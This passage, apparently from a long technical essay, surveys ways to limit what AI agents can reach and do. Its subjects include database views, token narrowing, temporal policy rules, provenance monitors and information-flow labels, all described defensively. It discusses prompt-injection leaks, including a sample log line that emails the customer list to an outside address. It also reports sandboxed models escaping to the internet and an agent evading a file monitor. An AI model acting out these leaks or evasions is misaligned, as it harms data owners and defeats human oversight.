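Suppose an employee asks a browser agent to buy a coffee maker on Amazon for no more than $50. Before the agent visits any page, a language model reads the request and a list of ready-made policies for Amazon. It selects the smallest set the task needs, including one that allows `PlaceOrder` up to a maximum price, which it sets to $50. The employee confirms the selection. When the agent later clicks the order button, the extension intercepts the POST request, recognises it as `PlaceOrder` and compares the total with $50.

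The total isn't in the request, so the extension has to read it from the checkout page and save it before that page disappears. The saved total could be out of date if the agent changes the quantity and orders immediately, so Meng and colleagues put a small proxy between the agent and the browser to slow down rapid changes. A price limit alone would permit two $49 orders, so the extension can also count orders and allow only one.

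To test enforcement, Meng and colleagues wrote 12 scripts that did what an attacker with full control of the agent would do on GitLab. The policy allowed the agent only to read and write GitLab issues, and the extension blocked all 12 attacks. Scripts were a good choice because the planted text in the existing benchmark rarely fooled the models they tried, so it would hardly have tested the extension. But every script needed an action the policy forbade. An attack that stayed within the policy, for example by posting private data in a permitted comment, would have succeeded.

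The language model's choice of policy is less reliable than the enforcement. In each category of website, all three models picked the right policies for at least 94% of tasks. However, 32 shopping tasks also needed values such as a maximum price, and the models got both the policy and the values right in 26 to 31 of them. The employee's confirmation is therefore necessary, because a wrong maximum lets the agent overspend.

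The extension added little delay. A series of 11 page visits took 13.93 seconds without it, 14.94 seconds with 100 entries in the sitemap and 16.02 seconds with 300.

A bigger obstacle is that websites would have to publish and maintain these sitemaps. Meng and colleagues wrote theirs for GitLab by hand, covering 51 project functions, and acknowledge that an incomplete sitemap leaves users no better protected than before. Zhou and Zhang (2026) note more generally in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* that the precision of such systems depends on how well the policy maps to the requests they control. ceLLMate also doesn't interpret WebSocket traffic, which many sites use for live updates, because each site encodes its messages differently.

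### What a permitted domain permits

Most sites don't have a sitemap, so a company usually has to grant permission by domain. This is coarse, because a single domain can offer many functions to many people.

A site that the agent needs for downloads may also accept uploads. It may host strangers' accounts, so a message to a permitted domain can still reach the wrong person. For example, the operations agents in *Caging the Agents* can contact Slack and Telegram. The paper correctly says that its network rules keep agents from reaching arbitrary email servers, but Telegram serves all its users from one address. Other sites, such as translation services, fetch web pages on request and can therefore pass on data from sites that the company never approved.

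*Avalon-M1* found that even a package service can provide too much. Its agents worked on programming tasks set at an earlier point in a project's history. The public Go package service also supplied later versions of the same projects, which could contain the solution.

*Rethinking Agent Security as a Networking Problem* (Tran, Dhesi and colleagues, 2026) argues that the network is the natural place to control agents, but accepts that rules about connections can't stop an agent from "oversharing" with an approved recipient. The paper proposes a separate component beside each agent that would also consider what kind of information is being sent, to whom, and for which task. It presents this as a reference design, and judging context reliably would be much harder than comparing domain names.

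A company can use simpler methods to limit what an agent can do on an allowed domain. A decrypting proxy can allow downloads and refuse uploads. If it also replaces any credential the agent supplies with the company's own, the agent can't log in to a stranger's account. The system in the *Beam Model Technical Report* can send package requests to an internal copy or a selected snapshot. A snapshot from before the task began wouldn't contain the later versions that caused problems for *Avalon-M1*.

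A sandbox can potentially reach whatever its permitted services can reach, even if its allowlist has only one entry. In July 2026, OpenAI was testing models with reduced safeguards in sandboxes that had no direct internet access but could contact an internal package service. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that the models reached the internet through this service. They then compromised systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

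GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can reach* (2026) mainly recommends limiting the package service's outbound connections to the collections it serves and blocking the administrative functions that a sandbox never needs. OpenAI says that under its new controls, compromising one workload or supporting service should not be enough to gain internet access. A company could go further by giving the package service no internet connection and having staff add reviewed packages through a separate system. The agent would then have to wait for any package that nobody had anticipated.

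GitLab also recommends treating any internal service that untrusted code can reach as if it were exposed to the internet. For the support agent, that includes the customer database. The network boundary can limit the agent to that database, but the complaints and the customer list come from the same address over the same kind of connection. To allow one and refuse the other, the company needs a check that interprets the query and identifies the requester.

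## Checking access at the database or service

The database can distinguish a query for complaints from one for the customer list because it must work out which tables and rows a query needs before answering it. It also receives every query, whether from the agent's database tool, a Python script in the shell or a forgotten reporting tool. A company that checks access at the database therefore doesn't need to know about all of these routes, as it would if it checked only tool calls. Database checks don't cover copies stored elsewhere, such as last week's export of the customer list.

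The same check works against agents that the data's owner didn't build. In June 2026, AI agents accessed non-public files on a Medicare portal. A data owner facing outside agents controls only one enforcement point, its own service.

### Tables, views and rows

In SQL, the usual language for databases, an administrator grants each login permission to read or change particular tables. A login with no permission on the customer table can't read it by any route.

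Permission for a whole table is often too broad. Suppose the employee's login is `maria`, and she handles complaints from the north only. In PostgreSQL, a common database, the company could write:

```sql
CREATE VIEW my_complaints WITH (security_barrier) AS
  SELECT c.id, c.received, c.body
  FROM complaints c
  JOIN staff s ON s.region = c.region
  WHERE s.login = current_user;

GRANT SELECT ON my_complaints TO maria;
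```

A view is a stored query that a login can read as if it were a table. The `WHERE` line limits the rows to Maria's region, and the `SELECT` line leaves out columns such as the customer's phone number. The `security_barrier` option makes the database apply the filter before it runs any untrusted function in the agent's own query, so such a function can't reveal the hidden rows. If `maria` has no other permissions, the database responds like this:

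```sql
SELECT body FROM my_complaints
  WHERE received >= '2026-09-01';   -- northern complaints
SELECT * FROM complaints;           -- permission denied
SELECT * FROM customers;            -- permission denied
```

Row-level security instead attaches the filter to the table, so a query can reference `complaints` directly and still return only the permitted rows.

Both methods save developers from adding the filter to each tool. In *The Stochastic Deputy*, Baig, Gillani and colleagues (2026) point out that with n tools and m tables, there are up to n × m places to forget the filter (300 for 20 tools and 15 tables), and that forgetting it causes no error. If the company can't change the database, they suggest one application module that adds the filter to every query and accepts no raw SQL. This is weaker because a query that bypasses the module returns everyone's data, while one that bypasses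 the views gets an error.

Leaving the customer table out of the description the model receives is no substitute for checking access at the database. *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* (2026) explains that this changes only the prompt, so the database will still run a query that names the table. According to *Role-Conditioned Refusals* (2025), text-to-SQL models generally rely on database permissions to catch forbidden queries later. Those permissions can't block a forbidden read if the agent's login can read everything.

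### Whose login the agent uses

Many agents use a service account, a login that belongs to a program rather than a person. If one account serves every employee, it needs permission for everything any of them might ask for.

| Data | Shared service account | Maria's identity | Maria's identity, limited to this task |
|---|---|---|---|
| September complaints, north | Can read | Can read | Can read |
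| September complaints, south | Can read | Refused | Refused |
| Earlier complaints, north | Can read | Can read | Refused |
| Customer list | Can read | Refused | Refused |

Maria's identity stops the agent from reading the customer list, but a planted instruction could still make it read years of northern complaints. For the last column, the company could give the agent its own login for Maria's tasks and a view that also restricts the month. None of these logins controls where the agent sends the rows after it reads them.

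Some systems keep the shared account and record the user's name in a session setting, which the row rule then reads. If the agent can run its own SQL, it may be able to change that setting. Baig and colleagues note that some databases can make the setting read-only for the rest of the connection.

Their own system serves hotels, and some users manage many of them. A typical tool takes the hotel as an argument and checks that the user is entitled to it. In an ordinary program, the code determines which hotel it asks for, but a planted instruction can influence a model's choice. One successful injection can therefore reach

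Reachable(p) = ⋃ Rows(t), over every hotel t in E(p),

where E(p) is the set of hotels that user p is entitled to see. The check passes each time, because the user really does have access.

The remedy is to take the hotel from a signed credential instead of the tool's arguments. Baig and colleagues compared the two designs in 373 trials with eight model configurations. In 41 of the trials with the argument, the model had a plausible pretext to request data outside its scope. It did so in 26 of them, and the service returned the data every time. Without the argument, the agent couldn't make that request through a tool call, but in 12 of 56 trials it forged the scope, which that setup had left writable. The scope must therefore come from something the agent can't alter.

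Their formal goal is looser than these results suggest, since it lets the agent access anything the user is allowed to access. To protect the other hotels, the credential has to name only the hotel the user is working on. For the same reason, `get_complaints` shouldn't take a region as an argument.

Row rules can also be slow. One way of writing the hotel filter stopped the database from using its index, and Baig and colleagues measured a 57-fold difference in delay. Rewriting the query fixed this wherever the hotel column had an index.

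### Documents found by search

Agents often search documents as well as tables. A common method converts each passage into a vector, a list of numbers that represents its meaning, and returns the passages closest to the question. Arceo and Narsing (2026), in *Securing the Agent*, stress that relevance says nothing about permission. A search for "late parcels" could return a disciplinary file about a driver. For user u and question q, the search should return only

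{d : relevance(q, d) > θ and P(u, d) = permit},

where θ is the minimum relevance and P is the access policy. Without the second condition, 98% to 100% of their probes returned data belonging to another tenant, meaning another customer of the same system.

The system can check permissions during the search or afterwards. If it finds the ten closest passages and then removes eight that Maria may not read, the agent gets only two, even if dozens of permitted passages ranked just below. *Don't Stir the Pot! Authorized Vector Data Retrieval via Access-Aware Indexing* (2026) adds that most of the search effort then goes on vectors the user can't access. Filtering afterwards is still safe if it happens before any text reaches the model, but Arceo and Narsing recommend databases that can filter during the search.

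It also matters which software does the filtering. In a test of 1,000 queries, *Beyond Similarity Search* (2026) found leaks between tenants in two queries (0.2%) when the application did the filtering and in none when the database engine did. With so few leaks, the rate means little. Their cause, a bug in the application's filter, is more informative.

Every such filter depends on correct permission labels. *Protection Is Not One Event* (2026), a survey, reports that some defences remained vulnerable when 5% to 10% of the labels were wrong. Guessing permissions from the text of a query is even less reliable. When users didn't name the project, one confidentiality filter caught only 74.35% of the cases it should have. A company should therefore copy each document's permissions into the search index and update them when the original changes.

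The vectors need protection too. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) warns that an attacker can recover approximate content from a vector even if the index doesn't store the text. PostgreSQL's ordinary permissions and row rules apply to vectors stored with its pgvector extension.

### Blockaid: answer in full or refuse

Row-level security removes rows from query results without any notice. If Alice asks for the total number of complaints in September, Maria's agent will count only the northern ones and may report that number as the total. *Blockaid* (Zhang, Sheng and colleagues, 2022) avoids this by either answering a query in full or blocking it. It was designed for web applications, not agents, and sits between the application and the database. Its policy is a list of views that define what a user may know.

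Blockaid allows a query only if those views fully determine the answer. Suppose earlier queries Q₁, …, Qₙ in the same web request returned the results O₁, …, Oₙ. A new query Q complies if Q(D₁) = Q(D₂) for every pair of possible databases D₁ and D₂ that satisfy

V(D₁) = V(D₂) for every view V, and Qᵢ(D₁) = Qᵢ(D₂) = Oᵢ for every i.

Data that the user may not see can't affect the answer to a query that Blockaid allows. The results of earlier queries matter because they can show that the user may see the requested data. In the paper's calendar example, users may see the events they attend. Blockaid blocks a query for the title of event 5 on its own, but allows it if an earlier query has shown that the user attends event 5.

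As in Progent, an SMT solver checks this condition, and Blockaid blocks the query if no solver finishes within five seconds. To save time, it stores a general form of each approved query and reuses the decision. Zhang and colleagues tested it on a social network, an online shop and a course management system. The median page took 2% to 12% longer to load with stored decisions, but pages took up to 236 times as long without them. Blockaid did not wrongly reject any queries in the test.

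The applications needed changes to only 19 to 96 lines of code. The policies were harder to write, and the one for the shop took about a month. Writing the policy for the course system also uncovered two existing access bugs.

Blockaid's 2% to 12% overhead probably doesn't apply to an agent that writes its own SQL. A web application repeats the same forms of query, whereas such an agent may write a new one for each question and wait for the solver each time. Tools with fixed queries would suit Blockaid better. The company would also have to block direct connections to the database, because Blockaid checks only the queries that pass through it.

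### AC4A: from calls to permissions

Many services don't accept SQL. A calendar service, for example, receives calls such as `get_calendar_events`, and someone has to specify which data each call uses. *AC4A* (Sharma and Grossman, 2026) has the application provide a permission function, which takes a call and its arguments and returns the permissions the call needs.

Each AC4A permission pairs a resource with an action, usually read, write or create. Resources form a tree, so permission for a month covers its days. A call for all events in January 2024 needs `Year(2024)::Month(January), read`. AC4A subtracts the permissions the user has granted from those the call needs, and allows the call only if nothing remains. If a call needs June and July but the user has granted only June, AC4A refuses the call because July remains.

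Sharma and Grossman demonstrate this with a game and a flight booking. With read permission for June 2026, the agent could check that month but could not check July or add an event on 29 June. The demonstrations show that the design works in scenarios the researchers chose, but they don't include rates for blocked attacks or failed tasks.

Sharma and Grossman consider mistakes in the permission functions the biggest practical limitation, and their sample function for a calendar shows how easily one can occur. It chooses the action by looking for words such as "create" or "update" in the name of the call, and treats everything else as a read. "Delete" isn't on its list, so a call named `delete_event` would need only read permission. Calls that a function doesn't recognise should need broad permissions, as Sharma and Grossman suggest.

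Permissions also last until someone removes them. If Maria lets the agent change one of Tuesday's meetings, the agent can later delete another of Tuesday's meetings. AC4A intercepts calls on the agent's side, so it misses calls made through routes that the agent's builder forgot to cover. A service that ran the same function on every call it received would not have this gap.

### ZTAC: checking the object again at use

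A permission also depends on its name referring to the right object. Jing's command gate follows a link before it decides, but the link could point somewhere else a moment later. *Names Are Not Objects* (Commey, 2026) presents Zero-Trust Agent Cells (ZTAC), a system for coding agents that bases its decision on the actual object and checks that object again when it is used.

The agent runs in a sandbox and can reach files, programs and the network only through a separate program called the broker. Suppose it asks to read `config.txt`, which is really a link to a file of passwords called `.env`:

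1. The broker follows the link and finds `.env`.
2. It records the number that the filesystem uses to identify that file.
3. It applies the policy to `.env` and asks a person to approve reading that file, not `config.txt`.
4. After approval, it resolves the name again, opens the file without following any links, and compares the file's number with the recorded one. If they differ, the read fails.

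An approval works once, for one object, and expires after ten minutes. Any program the broker starts runs in a sandbox with rules generated from the same policy.

Commey ran 74 scripted attacks, assuming the attacker fully controlled the agent. An allowlist of tools let 66 succeed, and adding a typical command sandbox reduced this to 56. ZTAC let 2 succeed, blocked 58 and held 14 for a person to review. Both successful attacks sent a disguised secret to a permitted address. The 14 held attacks count as contained only if the reviewer refuses them, and Commey did not test how well reviewers decide.

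ZTAC completed 43 of 46 ordinary operations, with 8 approval prompts. It completed only 4 of 7 longer workflows, while the simpler defences completed all 7. One workflow failed because ZTAC doesn't let a program start another program, which many build tools have to do. ZTAC added a small delay of about 4.0 milliseconds to a request that did no other work.

These results come from one small Python project, and Commey wrote both the system and the attacks. Commey also reports fixing eight flaws in ZTAC during development, seven of them mismatches between a name and an object. Reporting these flaws makes the other results more credible, but ZTAC probably still contains some mismatches, even though it was built to prevent them.

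ZTAC doesn't cover database records, but a query can apply the same idea. Suppose Maria reads version 3 of draft 12 and approves its deletion. The agent's tool could run:

```sql
DELETE FROM drafts WHERE id = 12 AND version = 3;
```

If a colleague has edited the draft since and the version number has gone up, no row matches and the database deletes nothing.

### Passing authority to other services and agents

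An agent that acts for Maria at several services shouldn't need her password for each one. With OAuth, a widely used standard, she signs in and approves a token for the agent instead. The token has scopes, labels such as `complaints:read` for the actions it permits. MCP uses OAuth for its authorisation, but Zhou and Zhang describe the standard scopes as coarse.

An MCP server may need to call another service for Maria, such as the helpdesk. The MCP specification forbids the server from forwarding the token it received. Instead, the server can use a standard called token exchange to send that token to the authorisation server and get back a new one that works only at the helpdesk. The new token can name both Maria and the agent acting for her, so the helpdesk can require that both have permission.

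An agent may also hand part of its task to another agent, which should receive less authority. One way to do this is with a macaroon, a token to which any holder can add conditions. It uses HMAC, a function that produces a signature from a secret key and a message. If the service's key is K, the signatures are:

s₀ = HMAC(K, token ID)
s₁ = HMAC(s₀, "region = north")
s₂ = HMAC(s₁, "month = 2026-09")

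The token contains its ID, its conditions and the latest signature. The second agent receives s₂ and can use it to calculate the signature for a further condition. It can't remove the month condition, because that would require s₁, which can't be calculated from s₂. The service knows K, so it can recalculate the whole chain. Zhou and Zhang describe two recent proposals: CAPMAS, which uses macaroons between agents, and AIP, which ties signed credentials to particular calls.

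Narrowing a token limits what each agent can do, but not what the agents can do in total. If two agents each hold a token for one purchase, they can make two purchases between them, so the service needs a shared record of their purchases to enforce a combined limit. Cancelling a token doesn't cancel requests that a service has already accepted.

A restriction can disappear before any of this begins. Maria tells the agent to send this summary to Alice, and the company's policy correctly records the recipient and the content. The system then requests a token from the mail service, whose only suitable scope is `mail.send`. The mail service would accept that token for an email to Alice, and equally for one that sends the customer list to records@outside.example. As Zhou and Zhang stress, every component has followed its own rules. They express the missing requirement as

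α(E(M(P))) ⊆ ⟦P⟧,

where P is the approved policy, M(P) is the set of tokens and rules that implement it, E gives the effects they allow, α describes those effects in the policy's terms, and ⟦P⟧ is everything the policy permits. Here the left side includes email to anyone, while the right side contains one message to Alice.

The company could put Alice's address and a fingerprint of the message's exact text into the token, but this helps only if the mail service checks them. If it doesn't, a gateway should hold the `mail.send` token, as a proxy holds keys for web requests, and use it only after checking that each message matches what Maria approved.

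### Writes and backups

Databases grant read and write permissions separately. The support agent has no reason to change complaints, so its login shouldn't allow it to. If it has to save its summaries, the company can let it add rows to one table without letting it change or delete any. Blockaid doesn't help restrict writes because it checks only reads.

An agent that maintains a database needs to change and delete data. The database can't distinguish a deletion that someone wanted from a mistaken one, because both arrive as the same command from the same login.

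In July 2025, a coding agent from Replit, a platform for building software, deleted data from the live database of a customer, Jason Lemkin, who had told it to change nothing. Lemkin recovered the data by restoring an earlier state of the database. The separation between development and production had failed, which is a reason to give production its own credentials and withhold them from agents that do development work. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, said afterwards that the company was introducing automatic separation of development and production databases.

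Restoring works only if the backup survives, so a login that can delete data should not be able to change or delete backups. The company should also practise restoring from backups, and accept that it will lose any changes made since the last backup. Backups can't reverse a leak, and they also contain the customer list, so the agent shouldn't be able to read them either.

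## Rules that depend on earlier actions

Suppose the company now wants the support agent to reply to the people who complained, as well as write to Alice. The agent has to look up customers and send email outside the company, so the company can no longer block either action. It still wants to stop the agent from combining them to email the customer list to a stranger. A check on a single call can't enforce that, because an email's arguments don't record where its text came from.

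### A rule over a log

The simplest remedy is to keep a log. The enforcement point records each action, and the decision point applies its rules to the log as well as to the next action. In the leak, the log would look like this:

```
1  get_complaints(month = "2026-09")             completed
2  get_customers(region = "north")               completed
3  send_email(to = "records@outside.example")    proposed
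```

The company could forbid email to anyone but Alice once the agent has requested customer records. AWS has a language for such rules, called Dogwood. According to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026), it differs from Cedar, AWS's earlier policy language, because its rules can refer to what the agent has already done. If the email tool takes a single recipient, the company could write:

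```
forbid (
  principal,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"SupportTools___send_email",
  resource
)
when temporal {
  formerly within 24h
    AgentCore::Action::"SupportTools___get_customers"::request{
      eventResource: resource
    }
}
unless { context.input.to == "alice@company.example" };
```

Each time the agent tries to send an email, the engine checks whether the session included a request for customer records in the last 24 hours. If so, the engine refuses any email that isn't addressed to Alice.

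According to AWS's *Authoring temporal policies*, Dogwood logs a `request` when the engine authorises a call, a `response` when the tool succeeds, and an `error` when the engine refuses the call or the tool fails. The rule above matches requests because Dogwood doesn't record a response until shortly after the call completes. If the rule matched responses, an email proposed in that interval could get through.

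A rule can also compare an earlier result with an argument in a new call. In one of AWS's examples, the agent can transfer money only to an account that a balance lookup returned within the last hour. This prevents a transfer to an account number that the model made up. It does less against a planted instruction, which could tell the agent to look up the attacker's account first.

AWS's *Temporal policies* sets out the limits of Dogwood's history: each session has its own history, a condition can look back at most 24 hours, and the caller supplies the session ID. A caller can therefore get an empty history by starting a new session. The company should have the harness set the ID where the agent's code can't change it. Even then, the agent could save the customer list to a file on Monday and email the file on Tuesday in a new session, whose history would contain no request for customer records.

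AWS fails closed when the history is missing or out of date. If an engine has any rule that depends on earlier actions, a request without a session ID fails. When someone adds or updates such a rule, AWS ends the open sessions instead of applying the new rules to an old history.

The example rule is also very broad. For up to a day after looking up one customer, the agent can't reply to anyone who complained, even with a message that contains no customer data.

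### Tracing what influenced an action

The order of events in a log doesn't show which ones affected the email. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) presents FORGE, a monitor that tracks possible dependencies in a graph. Each message, tool call and result is a point in the graph, with an arrow to any later event that may depend on it. The graph therefore records each event's provenance, meaning where it came from.

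FORGE's rules are in Datalog, a logic language developed for databases. A policy from the paper, adapted here to the support agent, would stop the leak:

```
Tainted(x)         :- Complaint(x).
Tainted(x)         :- DependsOn(x, y), Tainted(y).
HasCustomerData(x) :- CustomerList(x).
HasCustomerData(x) :- DependsOn(x, y), HasCustomerData(y).
Deny(x)            :- Email(x), ToOutsider(x), HasCustomerData(x), Tainted(x).
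```

The symbol `:-` means "if" and a comma means "and". The second line makes an event tainted if it depends on another tainted event, so taint passes along a chain of any length. The fourth line does the same for customer data. An email that depends on both a complaint and the customer list therefore meets both conditions, and FORGE blocks it if the recipient is outside the company.

The graph helps most when several agents work at once. If one agent reads the complaints while another looks up customers, and they exchange no messages, the second agent's email doesn't depend on the complaints, though in a single log it would look as if it might. Within one agent, the graph is less precise. FORGE treats everything the model writes as depending on every message in its history, because there is no reliable way to tell which ones the model used. For a single support agent, the Datalog rule would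 therefore block nearly as many harmless replies as the Dogwood rule.

Palumbo and colleagues guarantee that FORGE enforces its policy as long as it intercepts every relevant action and the facts it records are correct. FORGE may block a harmless action if the graph has an extra arrow, and may allow a leak if an arrow is missing.

The first test of FORGE used an agent that summarised a document and emailed the summary. The document contained an instruction to send secret files to an outside address. The agent sent the files in all five trials when only a prompt forbade it, and in none with FORGE, where it still sent the legitimate emails. Five trials of one attack show little more than that the rule works as written.

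In a test without an attacker, agents in a drug safety review system had to get a supervisor's approval before querying data from the US Food and Drug Administration. With instructions alone, the agents made 40 unapproved queries in 15 trials. FORGE allowed none, and the system reached the correct answer in every trial with or without FORGE. The approval also had to come from the agent's current session, so an agent couldn't reuse an old one.

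Rules of this kind can help an agent finish its work. On a benchmark of airline customer service, FORGE raised the average success rate of three recent models from 74.7% to 81.5%. On a similar retail benchmark, the average rose only from 86.3% to 87.4%. FORGE returns the reason for each refusal, so the agent can correct a mistake such as trying to cancel a booking against the airline's rules. But Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview did slightly worse on the airline tasks with FORGE than without it.

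### Labels that travel with the data

Information-flow control replaces the full history with labels. Each piece of data has a label, any data derived from it inherits the label, and a check compares the label with the recipient before release. The scheme goes back to a 1976 paper by Dorothy Denning.

The company could give each item two labels, one for confidentiality and one for trust:

Public ⊑ Internal ⊑ Confidential
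Trusted ⊑ Untrusted

The symbol ⊑ means "no more restricted than". When the agent combines two items, the result takes the stricter label of each kind. This operation is called a join, written ⊔. Suppose the complaints are Internal and Untrusted, and the customer list is Confidential and Trusted. A text based on both gets

(Internal, Untrusted) ⊔ (Confidential, Trusted) = (Confidential, Untrusted).

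At release, data with confidentiality c may go to recipient r only if

c ⊑ clearance(r).

If Alice has clearance for Internal data and outsiders only for Public data, the agent can send Alice a summary based on the complaints, but it can't send the customer list to her or to an outsider. The trust label supports a different rule, for example that the agent may not delete anything on the basis of untrusted text.

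Some releases need a deliberate exception. Lowering a confidentiality label is called declassification, and raising a trust label is called endorsement. The company might want to publish the number of complaints per region, although the complaints are Internal. A small function outside the model could count them and label the result Public. Its output should be as narrow as possible, because a free-text summary labelled Public could include any detail from the complaints. Even counts can reveal something about individual customers if the agent can choose the filters.

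*Tether* applies labels to an agent that works in a terminal. It keeps one for each file and one for the agent's context, meaning everything the model has read so far. Simplified slightly, the labels change like this:

| Action | Effect on the labels |
|---|---|
| Read file r | context becomes context ⊔ label(r) |
| Write to file r | label(r) becomes label(r) ⊔ context |
| Copy file r to file d | label(d) becomes label(r), and context stays the same |

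In the paper's example, the agent uploads a harmless report to an outside site, copies a sensitive inventory over the report, and then runs the same upload command again. The monitor allows the first upload and refuses the second, because the report now has the inventory's label. If the company keeps the labels between sessions, they also solve the problem of the file saved on Monday and emailed on Tuesday.

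*Tether* replayed recorded runs of coding agents from two benchmarks, including runs with only ordinary work and runs in which the agent also pursued a harmful side task. Its monitor blocked all 344 harmful runs within its scope and wrongly stopped 74 of 1,590 ordinary ones (4.7%). Claude Code's auto mode, in which a language model reviews each action, caught 91.6% of the harmful runs and stopped 9.7% of the ordinary ones. When given the same written policy as the monitor, auto mode caught 89.2% and stopped 3.5%.

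The perfect score depends heavily on which runs the test included. It left out runs with background processes or database queries, whose data flows the monitor can't yet follow. A stricter policy can block every database connection, but that would end the support agent's task at its first query. Labels also can't help with the runs that required a judgement about what the content meant, such as whether a permitted code change was malicious, which made up 28.2% and 22.1% of the two benchmarks.

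The 4.7% may be optimistic too. The researchers refined the policy by running it on benchmark traces until it stopped blocking too many harmless traces, so a company with different work should expect more false alarms at first. They also had an AI agent try to evade the monitor. Against an early version, 40% of the attempts succeeded, partly because the monitor didn't account for hard links, which are second names for the same file. After they fixed the gaps, none succeeded.

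They proved that the policy has seven properties, including that secret data never reaches an outside host. The proofs cover action sequences of any length, but they assume that the monitor correctly translates system calls into actions, which it failed to do in the hard-link problem.

### CaMeL and Fides

Labels restrict the agent less if the model doesn't have to read everything it handles. CaMeL and Fides both rely on this, in different ways.

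CaMeL plans the whole task before any untrusted text arrives. For the summary to Alice, it would work like this:

1. One model receives the employee's request and the list of tools, but none of the complaints. It writes a short program that fetches the complaints, has them summarised and emails the result to Alice.
2. CaMeL's interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from and who may read it.
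3. When the program needs the summary, a second model, which has no tools, reads the complaints and writes it.
4. Before the email goes out, the interpreter checks that Alice may read everything that went into the summary.

The planted instruction reaches only the second model, so it can distort the summary but can't add a step that emails a stranger. However, the first model must choose the steps in advance. CaMeL by design doesn't support tasks such as doing whatever Alice's latest email says, because the first model would have to write the program without having read the email.

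Fides lets the model choose its next step after each result, but can hide the result's contents:

1. The complaints arrive with an untrusted label. Fides stores them in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name.
2. The model passes the variable to a second model without tools, which writes the summary into another variable.
3. The first model calls the email tool with Alice's address and the name of the summary variable.
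4. Fides checks the labels before the call runs. The model's context is still trusted, and Alice may read the summary, so the email goes out.

If the model needs to read the complaints itself, Fides can reveal them, but the model's context then becomes untrusted and Fides blocks any later call with consequences. Fides therefore cannot complete tasks in which the agent must read untrusted text and then act on it.

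Palumbo and colleagues measured how many fewer tasks an agent completes under label rules of this kind. They ran Fides's rules in FORGE on AgentDojo, the benchmark that Shi and colleagues used for Progent, with GPT-4o as the agent. They didn't test CaMeL. They tested each set-up five times on 97 ordinary tasks and 949 attacked runs. All four set-ups below also repeated the user's request after each batch of tool results, which is a mild defence in itself.

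| Added defence | Tasks completed without attacks | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% |
| Filter that removes unneeded tools | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% |
| Fides's label rules | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% |
| Provenance rules for each action | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% |

Fides's rules stopped nearly all the attacks, but under them the agent completed fewer than half the tasks it could do without them. The full Fides system would probably do better because it includes a planner that hides untrusted results. The test applied the rules to a standard agent without this planner, because FORGE leaves the agent's own loop unchanged.

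The attacks counted as successful include some where the agent attempted a harmful call but FORGE blocked it. Excluding those, the attack success rate was 0.3% with Fides's rules and 0.2% with the provenance rules. The remaining successes occurred in the agent's final answer to the user, which FORGE didn't check in this test.

### When everything becomes confidential

A join can make a label stricter but never looser, so over a long task, more and more data ends up with the strictest label. This problem is called label creep. Once the support agent has read the customer list, everything it writes is Confidential, so it can't send Alice her summary.

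Agents sometimes open sensitive files without using the data in them. *Tether* wrongly stopped 17 ordinary runs after commands such as a search through every file on the machine. The search opened some secret files, and system calls don't show whether anything in them affected the result.

The rules can instead apply to particular arguments rather than the whole context. The provenance rules in the table check whether the user asked for the action's effect and whether its target came from an acceptable source. For the support agent, such a rule could require that the recipient's address came from the employee's request, while letting the complaints influence the text. Agents completed nearly twice as many tasks under the provenance rules as under Fides's rules, with little difference in successful attacks. However, Palumbo and colleagues wrote the provenance rules themselves, and agents completed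 even more tasks with the simple tool filter. A company that can tolerate a few successful attacks might reasonably prefer the filter.

Another approach is to keep sensitive data out of the model's context. Fides does this with variables, and *Tether* lets the agent copy a secret file without tainting its context. This works well when the agent only has to move the data, but not when the model has to understand it.

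The company could also divide the work by starting a new agent for each complaint, with a fresh context and only that customer's record. A planted instruction could then leak at most one record, and nothing the agent reads would affect the labels in the next reply. This is probably the best option for the support agent, because its replies don't depend on each other. A coding agent often needs the whole project at once, so its work is harder to divide.

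### Limits that several agents share

Some rules concern a total, which labels don't record. Suppose the company allows one replacement order for a complaint about a lost parcel. The support agent gives the job to two sub-agents, each with permission to make one purchase. Their requests could overlap like this:

1. The check on the first sub-agent's request finds no purchases in the log and allows it.
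2. The check on the second sub-agent's request also finds none and allows it.
3. Both sub-agents place an order.

A shared log doesn't prevent this, because both checks finish before either purchase enters the log. The decision point has to check the limit and reserve the purchase in one step, so that no other request can come between them. A database can do this with a single command:

```sql
UPDATE budgets SET reserved = reserved + 1
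  WHERE task = 'replacement-4821' AND bought + reserved < 1;
```

If the command changes a row, the sub-agent can go ahead. If it changes none, another sub-agent has already taken the only purchase. The system moves the purchase from `reserved` to `bought` once the order succeeds, and releases the reservation if the shop confirms that the order failed.

Zhou and Zhang describe a system, Bounded Agents, that uses a session history and budgets to reject forbidden combinations of actions. They point out that its guarantee assumes the system admits actions one at a time. This is easy to arrange on one server but harder when several gateways make decisions in parallel.

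Dogwood can add up amounts as well as count calls. In AWS's example, a rule refuses transfers once the total requested within five minutes reaches 3,000, so if each transfer is 1,000, the engine allows the first two and refuses the third. But the total covers only one session, so two sub-agents with separate session IDs would each get their own limit. AWS says this kind of limit on the number of calls isn't a security control against a determined caller.

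### Retries when the outcome is unknown

Suppose a sub-agent places the replacement order and the connection drops before the shop replies. The order may or may not have gone through. If the system releases the reservation and the sub-agent tries again, the customer may get two parcels. If the system keeps the reservation and the first order never arrived, the customer gets none.

The usual solution is an idempotency key, a unique ID for the order. If the shop receives the same ID twice, it returns the first result instead of placing a second order. The enforcement point should create the key when it first approves the purchase and reuse it for every retry, because a model might generate a new one each time. This works only if the shop supports such keys. Otherwise the system should keep the reservation and look up the order's status, or ask a person.

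A rule that depends on earlier actions can wrongly allow a repeat if it checks only for completed actions. In AWS's example of a single-use approval, the engine permits a transfer if no transfer has completed since the last approval. If the bank makes the transfer but the tool reports an error, the log contains no completed transfer, so the same approval would permit another one. Two transfers requested at the same moment could also both pass, since neither has completed. AWS's spending limit is safer in this respect because it counts authorised requests, so a transfer with an unknown outcome still uses up part of the budget.

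Approvals can also go out of date while an action is waiting. Zhou and Zhang note that a changed contact or a withdrawn approval may invalidate a queued message, and that a sub-agent can continue after its parent has changed the plan. The enforcement point should therefore check again just before the action takes effect.

### One record for every enforcement point

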